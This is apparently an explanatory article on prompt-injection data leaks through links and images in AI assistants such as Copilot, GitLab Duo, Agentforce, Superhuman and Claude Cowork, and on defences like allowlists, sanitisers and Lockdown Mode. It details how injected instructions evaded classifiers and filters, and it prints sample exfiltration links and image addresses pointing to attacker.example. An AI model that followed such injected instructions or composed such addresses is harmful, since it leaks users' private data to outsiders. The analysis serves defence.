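An application that bans images can still show diagrams if it draws them from text. In March 2025, before Mayraz found the flaw, GitHub announced a preview of Copilot Chat that displays diagrams in a side panel. GitHub's *Instant previews, flexible editing, and working with issues in Copilot* (2025) suggests asking for a diagram of a project's commits, the saved changes to its code. Copilot writes such diagrams in Mermaid, a text notation for boxes and arrows, and the page draws them without loading a picture from another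 server. The drawing code must also block outside images, because a diagram that can include them would allow the same leak.

Users can also still attach images and PDFs to their questions, including on GitHub's website, according to GitHub's *Copilot vision is generally available* (July 2026). A developer can upload a screenshot of an error and get a written explanation. This doesn't require Copilot to load an image from an address that the model wrote, so GitHub can offer it without allowing images in answers.

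Neither account of the August fix mentions links. Removing images would not have stopped Mayraz's first demonstration, which used a link.

### Lockdown Mode in ChatGPT

OpenAI made removal optional. On 13 February 2026 it introduced Lockdown Mode, a setting that limits ChatGPT's contact with the web and other outside services. It was first available in ChatGPT's Enterprise, Edu, Healthcare and Teachers plans, where an administrator could assign it to particular people. On 4 June OpenAI began extending it to personal accounts and to business accounts that customers set up themselves.

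OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) says the setting is for a small group of highly security-conscious users, such as executives and security teams at prominent organisations, and is "not necessary for most users". The help page, OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode*, now describes the intended users more broadly, as people and organisations that handle sensitive data and want stricter protection. As of early December 2026, it lists these restrictions:

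| Feature | What Lockdown Mode changes | What remains |
|---|---|---|
| Web browsing | No live pages | Stored copies, which may be old or missing |
| Images | ChatGPT may not show them in regular answers or retrieve them from the web | Image uploads and image generation |
| Deep research, which compiles long reports from many sources | Unavailable | – |
| Agent mode, in which ChatGPT carries out tasks on websites | Unavailable | – |
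| Canvas, a workspace for writing and code | Users can't let generated code access the network | – |
| File downloads | ChatGPT can't download files to analyse | Analysis of files the user uploads |

The browsing restriction blocks the kind of leak Tenable found in Gemini, because ChatGPT can only look for a stored copy and the request never leaves OpenAI's network. The restriction is a problem for users who need current information, such as a train time or today's price.

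The table doesn't list clickable links. OpenAI handles them with its separate protections against data leaks through web addresses, and Lockdown Mode adds to those protections rather than replacing them. A user in Lockdown Mode may therefore still receive links to sources, even though ChatGPT can't open the live pages.

Lockdown Mode's limits on connected apps depend on the type of account. On personal and self-managed business accounts, it blocks apps from accessing outside services live or making changes when this would conflict with its protections. ChatGPT's finance feature and shopping agents don't work. In larger organisations, administrators decide which apps stay on, and Lockdown Mode doesn't automatically disable all of them. OpenAI advises administrators not to let an app write anything unless they are sure an attacker couldn't see the result. An organisation that ignores this advice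 could turn on Lockdown Mode and still let ChatGPT post private data where an outsider can read it. The mode also doesn't change network access in Codex, OpenAI's programming assistant.

OpenAI keeps Lockdown Mode optional because of the features it removes. According to The Next Web's *OpenAI adds Lockdown Mode to ChatGPT to block data theft*, ChatGPT loses most of what makes its agent and research features useful. A lawyer reviewing an uploaded contract may hardly notice the restrictions, but a journalist researching today's news would lose much of the product. OpenAI thinks some users will accept the risks of connected features and should be able to choose them. It labels some of these features "Elevated Risk" and plans to remove each label once the safeguards are good enough for general use.

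Users with personal or self-managed business accounts can also turn Lockdown Mode off for a single chat. The lawyer could keep it on for contracts and turn it off to plan a holiday. But the mode doesn't change ChatGPT's memory, so if memory is on, details saved from a protected chat could be available in an unprotected one. To prevent that, she would need to manage her memory settings separately.

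OpenAI calls the mode deterministic but warns that data could still leak. Both can be true, because a fixed rule can reliably turn off live browsing without affecting an app that an administrator has left on. OpenAI also lists unforeseen combinations of features and newly discovered techniques as remaining risks. The mode doesn't stop injections themselves, so a hidden instruction in the lawyer's contract could still make ChatGPT describe an unfavourable clause as harmless.

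## Why did the filters in Microsoft 365 Copilot and GitLab Duo fail?

Most assistants keep links and images and rely on filters to remove the unsafe ones. Microsoft 365 Copilot and the programming assistant GitLab Duo both had such filters, but researchers still got private data out of both assistants in three attacks published in 2025 and 2026. They described the attacks in enough detail to show which part of each filter failed.

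### EchoLeak: a link style the filter missed

The security company Aim Security found EchoLeak in January 2025, after about three months spent working out how Copilot operates, according to Goldman (2025), in *New Microsoft Copilot flaw signals broader risk of AI agents being hacked*. The attack started with an email from outside the company. Copilot had four protections that could have stopped it or exposed it:

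- a classifier that looked for injections in incoming text
- a filter that removed links to outside websites from Copilot's answers
- a Content Security Policy (CSP) that limited where images could load from
- references that showed the employee which sources an answer used

The classifier missed the email because the instructions in it seemed to be addressed to the employee. Ravia (2025), who leads the research team that found the flaw, explains in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* that the text never mentioned AI, assistants or Copilot. Ravia thinks such classifiers are hard to train because there are few good collections of real injections, which can be written in any tone or language and on any topic. A stricter classifier might also flag legitimate mail, since colleagues often ask each other to collect information.

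The email then had to get into the model's context. Copilot searches for material relevant to the employee's question, and a short email about one subject would match only a few questions. The researchers therefore wrote a long email with many sections, each with a heading on a subject employees ask about, such as onboarding or leave, followed by the same instructions. Copilot could then retrieve the matching section when the employee asked about one of those subjects. In the attack Reddy and Gujral describe, the employee asks Copilot a question first, although Goldman writes that Copilot scans email in the background.

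The link filter missed reference-style links, which put the address elsewhere in the text. It also missed a shorter version of that style, in which the link's own words serve as the reference:

    [Open the full summary]

    [Open the full summary]: https://attacker.example/s?d=Offer%204.2%20million

Copilot's page displayed this as a working link, so the data leaked if the employee clicked it. The filter also missed the image version of this notation.

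The CSP blocked the image at first because it didn't permit the researchers' server. But the policy that Ravia reproduces had 29 different entries, and eleven were wildcards, which permit every subdomain of a domain. The researchers searched the permitted domains for a service that would fetch any address given to it. They found one in SharePoint, Microsoft's document-sharing service, but it worked only if the employee accepted an invitation to the attacker's SharePoint site. A second one, in Microsoft Teams, needed no invitation. With placeholder domains, the image address looked like this:

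    https://previews.example.com/fetch?url=https://attacker.example/Offer%204.2%20million

The browser sent the request because `previews.example.com` was on the policy's list. Microsoft's server then requested the second address, which contained the private text.

The fourth protection failed because the email contained an instruction to its recipient never to refer to it, supposedly for compliance reasons. Copilot followed this instruction and left the email out of its references. According to Reddy and Gujral, the employee would have noticed only what looked like a broken link or image.

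The attack could leak anything in Copilot's context, including the conversation so far and any emails, files or Teams chats Copilot had fetched. It couldn't copy the whole mailbox at once, but the attacker instructed the model to pick the most sensitive item it could find, so the attacker didn't need to know in advance what the employee had.

Microsoft first tried to fix the flaw in April 2025 and found related problems in May. Reddy and Gujral date the full fix to May. Aim and Microsoft made the flaw public on 11 June. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025), an entry in a Spanish government agency's vulnerability database, rates its severity at 9.3 out of 10. Microsoft said the flaw had affected no customers. Aim's cofounder Adir Gruss told Goldman that five months was a very long time for such a fix, and that it took that long partly because Microsoft had to find the right teams and explain a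 new kind of flaw to them.

In its statement to Goldman, Microsoft didn't explain what it had changed. Reddy and Gujral write that Copilot now strips reference-style links and embedded images from incoming outside content. Stripping them can't be a complete fix, because the model can also write a link that wasn't in any email. Reddy and Gujral add that Microsoft reportedly introduced options to stop Copilot from using outside messages in some situations. Copilot might then ignore relevant information, such as a supplier's quote that arrived by email.

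It isn't clear whether a company could have protected itself by changing Copilot's settings before the fix. Aim's web page on EchoLeak says that organisations can configure Copilot to ignore outside emails, but Ravia's article says that, as far as the team knew, no administrator setting could have prevented the attack.

### SearchLeak: a filter that ran too late

A year later, researchers at Varonis used a flaw in the timing of Copilot's output filter to extract data (*SearchLeak*, 2026). They attacked Copilot Enterprise Search, which searches a company's mail, calendars and files. In the attack, an employee clicked a link to Microsoft's own website. The part of the address that normally holds a search query contained the attacker's instructions, and Copilot followed them as if the employee had typed them.

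These instructions told Copilot to find an email and put its title in the address of an HTML image. Microsoft had anticipated dangerous HTML in answers. Its page placed the finished answer in a code block, so that the browser would display any HTML as text instead of loading an image. But the page also streamed the answer, displaying it while Copilot was still writing. The events happened in this order:

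1. Copilot began writing an answer that contained the image.
2. The browser displayed the unfinished answer and immediately requested the image.
3. Copilot finished writing.
4. The page put the answer in a code block, which turned the image into harmless text.

By the fourth step, the request had already left the browser. Programmers call this a race condition, a flaw in which the outcome depends on which of two events happens first. The attacker didn't need precise timing, because the image only had to be complete before the answer ended.

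The CSP would still have blocked a request to the attacker's server, so the image address pointed to Bing. Bing's "Search by Image" feature fetches a picture from a given address to analyse it. The policy permitted all Bing subdomains, so the browser sent the request, and Bing's server then contacted the attacker's server with the email title in the address.

The Bing wildcard was already in the policy that Ravia reproduced in 2025, so SearchLeak worked without anyone adding a risky new domain. Bing also made the final request in one of the ReLeak attacks.

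The demonstration took only an email title, but titles can contain login codes. The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox* says these codes often stay valid for several minutes. Copilot could also search the text of emails, meeting notes and any indexed company files the employee had permission to open.

Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), an advisory dated 4 June, rates the flaw critical. The flaw's numerical score is 6.5 out of 10, which The Next Web attributes to the attack requiring a click. Microsoft said that it had fully mitigated the flaw, that it knew of no exploitation, and that customers did not need to do anything. Varonis published the details on 15 June.

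The advisory doesn't identify which weakness Microsoft fixed. According to Varonis, the attack needed the instructions in the search address, the late filter and the Bing relay. Fixing any one of them would have stopped SearchLeak, but the other two could still have been used in a different attack.

EchoLeak used reference-style Markdown and Teams, while SearchLeak used HTML and Bing. Microsoft could therefore have completely fixed its handling of reference-style Markdown and still been open to SearchLeak. The Next Web wrote that three Copilot attacks, including these two, had each bypassed protections that the previous fix was supposed to establish, but the published details don't show this.

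### GitLab Duo: a sanitiser designed for a different attack

GitLab, like GitHub, is a website where developers store and discuss code. Its assistant, Duo, answers questions about a project and can read whatever the person asking has permission to read. In 2025, Duo's sanitiser didn't treat ordinary images as dangerous.

GitLab had received a warning about links a year earlier. In *Prompt injection in combination with markdown links in Duo Chat*, joaxcar (2024) reported on 15 March 2024 that a comment on a public issue (a discussion of a bug or planned change) could make Duo write a link containing text from a private issue. The victim had to ask about the public issue and then click the link, and the injection worked about one time in three. joaxcar thought the injection would be hard to prevent but that GitLab could easily reduce the risk from links by not displaying those with hidden addresses,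 permitting only certain domains, or showing a warning before opening an outside site.

Omer Mayraz, who later found CamoLeak, showed that Duo could leak data without a click. Legit Security's *Remote Prompt Injection in GitLab Duo Leads to Source Code Theft* describes how instructions hidden in a public project's code made Duo fetch code from one of the victim's private projects. Duo encoded the private code and put it in an image address, and the victim's browser sent it to the researchers' server without a relay like Teams or Bing. Legit Security says the same technique could leak confidential issues, including reports of security flaws not yet made public.

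Duo displayed its answers line by line, so its page interpreted the Markdown before the answer was complete. The researchers found that the page could treat HTML inside a link's text as real HTML while the answer was streaming, and they used this to insert an image.

The answer also went through DOMPurify, a widely used sanitiser that is good at removing HTML that could run an attacker's code in the page. By default, though, it keeps images, forms and links. Those defaults make sense on a website where people post comments with pictures, but in Duo the image request could carry private data. The default settings of the renderer markdown-it have the same limitation.

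According to Legit Security, the filter, DOMPurify, ran but kept the image because its default rules allowed images. Willison (2025), in *Remote Prompt Injection in GitLab Duo Leads to Source Code Theft*, instead describes streaming the answer as a way to bypass the filter. Waiting for the complete answer might have prevented the page from mistaking the link text for HTML, but it would not have made DOMPurify remove an ordinary HTML image.

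Legit Security reported the flaw on 12 February 2025. On 7 April, GitLab released a fix in Duo's interface software that makes the chat window sanitise links before displaying them. In an account published on 22 May, Legit Security says that Duo no longer displays images or forms that point to domains outside gitlab.com. Legit Security also says that GitLab fixed the injection, but doesn't explain how.

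The sanitiser leaves alone links to GitLab's documentation, gitlab.com and the customer's own GitLab site. It processes links to other websites, even ones a developer asked for, such as a link to the manual for a third-party code library.

GitLab's tests for the change cover more notations than Copilot's filter recognised. They include Markdown links, HTML links and bare URLs, inside and outside code blocks, and a link surrounded by stray backslashes and backticks. One test repeats part of joaxcar's attack almost word for word, so the fix probably addressed joaxcar's report too, nearly thirteen months after GitLab received it.

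Willison noticed a function in the fix called `isRelativeUrlWithoutEmbeddedUrls()`. A relative URL leaves out the domain, so it normally leads to another page on the same site. The function's name suggests that it also rejects URLs that contain another URL. The Teams and Bing relays both used URLs of that kind.

### The filter and the page must agree on what counts as a link

Copilot's link filter failed in EchoLeak because it recognised fewer kinds of link than the page did. Programmers call this a parser mismatch, meaning that two pieces of software interpret the same text differently. A developer can add the missing notation to the filter, but the filter may still miss another that the page recognises.

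Mozilla noticed the problem while developing AI Window, a chat feature for its Firefox browser. In *Add rendering-layer URL validation for AI Window chat messages*, rconcepcion first planned to search the model's raw text for addresses, with separate patterns for Markdown, HTML and bare addresses. The developer abandoned that approach in January 2026 because of a "two-parser conflict", in which the checker and the Markdown renderer could identify different text as clickable links.

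The new design checked the links that the renderer had produced. It disabled all of them, compared their addresses with a list of trusted ones and re-enabled only those on the list. An unusual notation can't get past this check, because the renderer has already turned every notation into the same kind of link. If the check hit an error, the links stayed disabled, whereas the earlier version would have displayed the answer anyway.

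Checking every message separately delayed the point at which links became clickable. rconcepcion then changed the design so the browser sends the list of trusted addresses to the chat page in advance. The page can then check each link while displaying it, without waiting for a reply from another part of the browser. The change shipped in Firefox 150.

The sanitiser has to check images even earlier, because a browser may request an image as soon as the page creates the element for it. The check therefore has to run on the parsed answer before the browser turns that answer into live content.

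Mismatches can also occur after a sanitiser has parsed the text correctly. DOMPurify can return the cleaned HTML as text, which the browser then parses again. *Safe DOM manipulation with the Sanitizer API*, on web.dev, warns that the second parse wastes processing time and can cause vulnerabilities if its result differs from the first. The Sanitizer API is intended to be built into browsers and make the second parse unnecessary.

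A filter also has to match how the application will display the text. In Markdown, backticks around an HTML image tag mark it as code, so the page shows the tag instead of loading the image. If another page displays the same text as HTML, the backticks are ordinary characters and the image loads.

The filter described in *HostnameFilter Service*, part of the documentation for the website software Drupal, handles this by assuming the riskier case. By default, it checks HTML even between backticks, so it can damage harmless code examples. Developers whose applications display Markdown can turn on a setting that preserves these examples, but the setting needs an additional Markdown parser. Without that parser, the filter still treats the examples as HTML.

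### Checking an answer while it is still arriving

After SearchLeak, Varonis recommended sanitising text at the moment the page displays it. A developer might therefore run the filter on each new piece of a streamed answer. But a piece can end in the middle of an address:

    Piece 1:  ![logo](https://attac
    Piece 2:  ker.example/logo.png?d=Offer%204.2%20million)

If an attacker splits an image's code between two pieces of a response and the filter checks each piece separately, the browser can still load the image once the page joins them. Chrome for Developers therefore recommends checking all the text received so far. The check has to finish before the page displays the new text.

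Repeating this work for every piece can slow down the page. Chrome for Developers warns that replacing the page's entire HTML each time new text arrives is slow, especially for answers with complex formatting, and leaves the page open to injection. It suggests a streaming Markdown parser to avoid the slowdown.

The application can also hold back an unfinished link while the rest of the answer continues to appear. The online shopping company Shopify built a Markdown parser that does something similar for its assistant, Sidekick, to stop half-finished formatting from disrupting the display. The same technique could let a security filter inspect the complete address before the link appears.

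Unfinished content is safer if the page keeps it inactive until the check is complete, as Firefox did with links. In SearchLeak, Copilot's page instead displayed active HTML first and deactivated it at the end. GitLab faced a related question with streamed code examples, which often appear before their closing mark arrives. GitLab's *feat(DuoChat): Add default markdown renderer for streaming messages* notes that the Markdown parser treats the end of the text as the end of any open code block. The page can then display an unfinished example as code from the start.

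Filtering a stream can cause different problems when another program reads the answer. Some applications ask the model for JSON, a structured data format that becomes invalid if a bracket or quotation mark is missing. Drupal's filter can't decode a single piece of streamed JSON on its own. According to Drupal's documentation, removing unsafe HTML from that piece may make the JSON invalid. Developers can turn off Drupal's special handling of JSON for a particular request.

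### Permitted servers that forward data

EchoLeak and SearchLeak also depended on permitted servers that would fetch an address for anyone. Varonis therefore recommends checking every permitted domain for services that fetch user-supplied addresses.

A service that fetches outside content can have an ordinary purpose. Bing has to fetch a picture from another website to analyse it, and Teams fetched outside content for previews. The danger came from allowing those services in a page where an attacker could influence the image addresses.

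Wildcards make the check much harder. If a policy permits every subdomain of `example.com`, the developer has to examine every service on them, including ones that other teams add later. Ravia called the search through Microsoft's permitted domains tedious, but it produced two working relays. Reddy and Gujral recommend avoiding wildcards and listing only the company's own servers that the application needs.

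## Does a list of trusted websites solve the problem?

An allowlist is a list of permitted domains or addresses, and the application blocks everything else. Browsers and sanitisers can use allowlists, and a network proxy can use one to decide which servers an AI agent's programs may contact.

Allowlists are popular because they are simple. The check is deterministic, and a security team can read a short list in a few minutes. In comments on a Claude tool that fetches web pages, Willison called a domain list much stronger than the tool's other protections, if nobody could use the listed domains to send data out. He added that choosing such domains is tricky.

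Microsoft's lists failed because Teams and Bing forwarded requests to the attacker. In four other attacks, published between September 2025 and January 2026, the data went to a domain on the list, where the attacker could collect it directly.

### Four listed domains that leaked data

Salesforce's AI product, Agentforce, can read the records of customers and possible customers (leads) that companies keep in Salesforce's software. Some of these records contain text from strangers, because a feature called Web-to-Lead creates a record when someone submits a form on a company's website. *Agentforce Web-to-Lead Vulnerability Exposed* (Martin, 2025) describes an attack, named ForcedLeak, in which the security company Noma put instructions in the form's description field. When an employee later asked Agentforce about that lead, it also followed Noma's instructions and put data from the records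 in an image address.

Salesforce's CSP should have blocked the image, but one of the permitted domains had expired. According to Hackread's *ForcedLeak Flaw in Salesforce Agentforce AI Agent Exposed CRM Data*, anyone could buy it for $5. The researchers registered it, and their server received the data. Paganini (2025), in *ForcedLeak flaw in Salesforce Agentforce exposes CRM data via Prompt Injection*, gives the flaw's severity as 9.4 out of 10. Noma said the leak would have been impossible without a way around the CSP, so an up-to-date list would have prevented it.

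Noma reported the flaw on 28 July 2025. Salesforce regained control of the domain and corrected its policy. On 8 September, it also began checking the addresses in its agents' answers against a list called Trusted URLs. That list can go out of date too, so someone still has to check that each domain belongs to the expected owner.

Checking ownership would not have protected Superhuman, an email app with an AI assistant. Its CSP permitted `docs.google.com`, where Google hosts online forms as well as documents. Anyone can create a form, and a link can fill in an answer and submit it in one step. With a placeholder domain, such a link might look like this:

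    https://forms.example.com/outsiders-form/submit?answer=Offer%204.2%20million

PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* describes how a hostile email made the assistant use a link of this kind as an image address. The user only had to ask for a summary of recent mail. When her browser tried to load the image, it submitted the form, and the attacker could read her emails in the form's responses. One of the assistant's answers leaked the full text of several emails, and another leaked parts of more than 40.

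PromptArmor, a security company, reported the flaw on Friday night, 5 December 2025. Superhuman disabled the affected features on Monday and released a first fix on Tuesday. It released more fixes until 11 January, the day before PromptArmor published its account. PromptArmor doesn't explain what the fixes changed, so Superhuman may have removed Google's domain from the list or restricted images in some other way.

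The list still made the attack harder. Superhuman Go, another assistant from the same company, loaded an image from the researchers' server, so they didn't need a form. PromptArmor used a Google form again in 2026 to extract emails from OpenAI's Codex, which by then handled office tasks as well as programming. PromptArmor's *Codex Exfiltrates Connector Data* says that OpenAI has fixed the flaw, but doesn't say whether Codex had a list of permitted image servers.

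Claude Cowork, an Anthropic product that works with files on the user's computer, runs code in a virtual machine, which is a simulated computer. The machine's network rules blocked almost every domain but made an exception for Anthropic's own API, the service through which other programs use Claude. This created a different problem, because an attacker can also have an account on that API.

PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* describes an attack in which the user gave Cowork access to a folder of property documents and uploaded a file containing hidden instructions. The instructions included the attacker's API key, a code that identifies an account. Claude used the key to upload a loan estimate to the attacker's account without asking the user for approval. The list of trusted websites didn't prevent this because the domain was trustworthy, even though the account receiving the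 data belonged to the attacker. The attack involved no links or images, but a list that restricts them can fail for the same reason.

PromptArmor published the attack in January 2026, two days after Cowork's release. It said Rehberger had already reported the same weakness in Claude's chat product, and that Anthropic had acknowledged but not fixed it. Apostol (2026) reported in *Anthropic Claude Vulnerability Exposes Cowork AI to Data Exfiltration via Prompt Injection* that Anthropic was updating the virtual machine. According to InfoQ (2026), Anthropic added a proxy that accepts only the access token issued for the user's own session. Cowork can still contact the API, but an attacker's key no longer works.

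The fourth attack used a domain that was unsafe from the start. Google's code editor Antigravity lets its AI agents control a browser, which is restricted to a list of permitted sites. The default list included Webhook.site, where anyone can create an address and see the requests sent to it. Developers use such services to test their programs, which may be why the site was on the list.

PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data* (November 2025) describes a developer who asked Antigravity to follow an online guide that contained instructions in tiny print. The model collected passwords and code from the project and opened a Webhook.site address containing them. The developer had accepted the recommended settings and might reasonably have assumed that Google had checked the list of trusted websites.

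Google showed new users a warning about data leaks. PromptArmor took this to mean that Google already knew of the risk, and published its findings without first reporting the flaw to Google. Willison noted that Google's page for security researchers listed such leaks as a known issue that the company was working to fix. Neither PromptArmor nor Willison says that Google removed Webhook.site from the list.

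### What a review of the list can find

A routine review could have found two of these four entries. A program can check every month whether a listed domain has expired, and a developer who knew what Webhook.site does would probably have removed it. The other two are harder to spot because most reviewers would accept a domain owned by Google or Anthropic.

The reviewer also has to work out what a stranger could do on each domain. For `docs.google.com`, she would need to know that it hosts forms as well as documents, and that an ordinary image request can submit an answer to a form. InfoQ concludes from the Cowork case that listing a domain grants access to every function reachable through it. The domain's owner can also add functions later without telling the companies that have listed it.

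Narrower entries reduce this work. GitHub lets administrators restrict its Copilot cloud agent to one folder on a server, such as `https://packages.example.com/project-1/`. A similar rule could have permitted Google's documents but not its forms. Restricting the folder would not have stopped the Cowork attack, because the attacker's files and the user's files go to the same address. Only the key is different, so Anthropic's proxy has to check the token.

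An administrator can also restrict the type of request. A browser normally uses a GET request to ask for a page or image, while a program typically uses a POST request to upload a file. The cloud version of Codex can block POST requests, which would stop many uploads. But the Google form accepted answers through GET requests, so blocking POST requests would not have protected Superhuman's users.

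### Harmless sites that the list leaves out

A short list is easier to check, but it blocks more harmless links and images. The maker of a general chatbot can't list every hotel and museum website in advance, and adding whole categories of websites would make the list much harder to check.

OpenAI argued in January 2026 that lists of trusted sites were not enough for ChatGPT, for two reasons. First, a trusted site can redirect visitors elsewhere. This is a problem for controls that, unlike CSP, check only the first address. Second, people visit far more than a handful of popular sites, so a strict list would produce frequent warnings about harmless pages, and users might learn to click through them without thinking.

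OpenAI gives no figures for how often a strict list would produce a warning. Its argument also applies only if the product warns users about unlisted addresses. If the product removes the link without asking, as Amazon Q did, users have no warning to ignore. OpenAI chose to check whether the exact address was already public instead of relying on a list of trusted sites.

Business users lose useful content too. When Salesforce began enforcing Trusted URLs, TechNadu's *Salesforce to Enforce Trusted URLs for Agentforce and Einstein AI* warned that agents might no longer be able to show images from other websites or link to another company's documentation. Links to outside feedback forms would also stop working until an administrator approved them.

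Developers can have trouble finding out why a request failed. In an October 2025 post on OpenAI's forum, *Codex with ‘unrestricted internet access’ are still hard-blocked by an internal allowlist*, a user complained that Codex could reach only common code sites even with unrestricted access turned on, and that other requests failed with the error "403 Forbidden". This is one user's account, and a configuration mistake is possible. GitHub's Copilot cloud agent is more helpful because it adds a warning to the proposed code change that shows the blocked address and the command that tried to reach it.

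### Who maintains the lists

Each Salesforce customer's administrators maintain its Trusted URLs list. Salesforce permits its own standard addresses, and the administrators add any others the agents need. Adding an address requires permission both to customise the application and to modify all data, so a salesperson who notices a missing link will usually have to ask someone else to restore it.

PromptArmor's *One key way Salesforce mitigates AI risk* explains that the Agentforce chat in Salesforce's web app replaces any web address that isn't on the trusted list with "[URL_REDACTED]". This applies to links and images, including addresses inside HTML and CSS. The list doesn't restrict the agent's tools. PromptArmor advises administrators to avoid wildcards that cover sites where strangers can post content, and to allow images from a domain only if the agent needs them.

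TechNadu notes that an approved address is permitted throughout the company's Salesforce system, not only in the agents' answers. An administrator who adds a domain to restore one link in an answer may therefore also allow other Salesforce pages to use it. Bullhorn's *SF Winter '25 Adopt Updated Content Security Policy (CSP) Directives*, a support article for recruitment software, warns that some embedded tools will stop appearing after a Salesforce update until an administrator adds their addresses to the same list.

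Even a vendor's own instructions can lead customers to add a risky address. Salesforce's newer assistant, Agentforce Coworker, also removes addresses by default, so customers who connect Google Drive have to add Google Drive's address to the list. Salesforce's *Add Trusted URLs for Agentforce Coworker (Beta)* gives the example `https://docs.google.com`, the domain used in the Superhuman attack. The same attack may not work in Coworker. The automatic leak shouldn't work if the administrator doesn't permit images from the domain, but a user could still submit a form by clicking a link.

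OpenAI and its customers share the work of choosing which domains Codex can reach. When Codex runs on OpenAI's servers, it has no internet access by default after the initial setup. A developer who turns access on can permit every domain, start with an empty list, or use a preset list of sites that programmers often download code from. OpenAI's *Agent internet access* says that finding the right domains may take "some trial and error".

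OpenAI promises to keep the preset list up to date so developers don't have to. But the list has about 70 domains, including `google.com`, `github.com` and `gitlab.com`. Anyone can open an account on these three, so a company handling confidential code would still need to consider what an attacker could do with one.

On a developer's own computer, Codex also starts with network access off. OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* explains that turning network access on gives commands unrestricted access unless the developer also turns on a network proxy. The proxy blocks every outside domain she hasn't allowed. In her list of allowed domains, `*.example.com` covers subdomains but not `example.com` itself, while `**.example.com` covers both.

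A company can set these rules centrally. A short configuration might look like this:

    [experimental_network]
    enabled = true
    managed_allowed_domains_only = true
    allowed_domains = ["packages.example.com", "docs.example.com"]
    denied_domains = ["uploads.example.com"]

The second line turns on the network rules. The third prevents developers from adding their own domains, and the last two list the domains Codex may and may not contact. If a domain matches both lists, Codex blocks it. These rules don't turn on network access by themselves.

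Administrators also need to check that every computer has received the rules. According to OpenAI's *Managed configuration*, Codex can download them when an employee signs in to a business account. If the download fails and Codex has no valid saved copy, it continues without the downloaded rules. A company that relies on the list should therefore also install the rules on each computer. OpenAI recommends checking regularly for differences between local settings and company policy.

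When OpenAI's own employees use Codex, it can contact expected domains automatically, can't contact certain others, and needs approval for unfamiliar ones (OpenAI, 2026). To reduce interruptions, OpenAI uses a second AI agent to approve some requests. The company also studies its logs to see how often the network rules block a request or require approval, and where the rules need adjusting.

OpenAI's example configuration automatically permits every subdomain of `openai.com`. Outsiders can have OpenAI accounts, so this raises the same question as Anthropic's entry for its own API. OpenAI requires employees to sign in to Codex through its company workspace, but it is unclear from the post whether the network proxy would block a request containing an outsider's API key.

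Claude Code, Anthropic's programming assistant, gives administrators less central control over the list of trusted domains. Anthropic says each cloud environment has its own list, and that administrators can't send one list to every employee's environment. They can create a shared environment with a standard list, but if a domain on many personal lists expires, each owner has to remove it separately.

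### Where a short list works

A short list works well for an internal assistant that cites only company pages. Suppose an employee asks how much parental leave she can take, and every source is on `wiki.example.com`. The company can allow that one address and remove all other links and images. She can still open the policy, so she loses very little.

The company should list only the wiki, not `*.example.com`, because another subdomain might host a public form. It also needs to make sure the wiki doesn't forward visitors to other sites, and that outsiders can't read its request logs or anything the assistant might submit there. These checks are manageable for one site that the company runs itself.

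The list becomes less convenient when employees also ask about suppliers' products or new laws. Glean, which makes a workplace assistant, lets administrators trust particular tools as well as domains. Its assistant keeps an address if a trusted tool returned it, it belongs to a trusted domain, or the user supplied it. So if a trusted search tool finds a supplier's manual, an employee can receive a link to it even if the supplier's website isn't on the list.

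## Can a product block only the addresses the model has composed?

In the attack on Superhuman's email assistant, the browser's policy permitted every address on `docs.google.com`, including the address of a Google Form with the text of the user's emails added to the end. The attacker could have published the form's address months earlier, but the model had to compose the complete address during the conversation because the attacker did not have the emails.

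The same is true of the image in the employee's answer. The outsider knew in advance that the address would begin with `https://attacker.example/logo.png?d=`, but not that the offer to Northgate was 4.2 million. An address containing data that an attacker couldn't predict must be new. A product can therefore allow addresses that existed before the conversation and block or question the rest, whoever owns the domain.

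Blocking only the addresses the model has composed can fail if the secret is short, or if the model can send it one character at a time. The attacker can then prepare an address for every possible value, so the model doesn't have to compose one. Mayraz did this in CamoLeak, with one image for each letter and symbol.

Blocking every address the model has composed also blocks many harmless ones. A link to flights on particular dates, for example, may have an address that never existed before. How often a product blocks harmless links depends on how it decides whether an address already existed. OpenAI looks for the address in an index of the public web, while Google and Anthropic rely on where the model got it.

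### OpenAI's check, from url_safe to a public index

In December 2023, OpenAI added an image check to ChatGPT's web version. The chat page loaded an image only if a service called `url_safe` approved its URL. Rehberger tried a URL that ended with an email address, and the service rejected it.

OpenAI didn't publish its criteria for which images ChatGPT would load. Anyone can read a website's Content Security Policy in the browser, but this check ran on OpenAI's server. Rehberger prepared 36 image addresses, one for each letter and digit, and nine loaded. According to Embrace The Red, `a.png` loaded but `d.png`, in the same folder, did not. Rehberger guessed that ChatGPT might be checking whether the addresses were in Bing's index.

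A year later, Tenable's researchers worked out one of the criteria. The service always approved addresses on `bing.com`. Bing's links to the sites in its index were addresses on its own domain that redirected visitors, so the researchers used the Bing links for their own sites, and ChatGPT displayed the images. In effect, `url_safe` contained a list of trusted domains, one of which had an open redirect. According to Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* (2025), the company reported the flaw on 10 December 2024 and was still asking for an update on 4 March 2025. OpenAI had not fixed it when Tenable published.

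Rehberger had presented similar bypasses at the Black Hat Europe conference in 2024. In 2025 he found another gap in the check, which he used to extract a user's chat history and memories. OpenAI made the check stricter around August 2025, which stopped the attacks he had demonstrated.

OpenAI also restricted the addresses that ChatGPT could open by itself while working on a task. After an attack called ShadowLeak, it allowed ChatGPT to open an address only exactly as received. This ban on composed addresses is the simplest form of the idea. The security company Radware got around it with a hostile email that contained a ready-made address for every letter and digit. ChatGPT opened the ones that spelled out the private text. Radware's *ZombieAgent* explains that the restriction didn't apply because ChatGPT never constructed an address.

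According to SecurityWeek, Radware reported the problem in September 2025 and OpenAI released a fix on 16 December. *ChatGPT falls to new data pilfering attack* (2026) reports that, after the fix, ChatGPT would open a link from an email only if the link was in a well-known public index or the user had supplied it in the chat. Previously, an exact copy of an address in an email was enough.

In January 2026 OpenAI explained the general rule in a post and a paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*. A crawler, a program that follows links from page to page, records the addresses it finds on the open web. Before ChatGPT loads an address automatically, it checks whether the crawler has already seen it:

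    ChatGPT is about to load an address.
      Did the user type this address in this chat?   -> load it
      Is this address in the public-URL index?       -> load it
      Otherwise -> try another website, or ask the user

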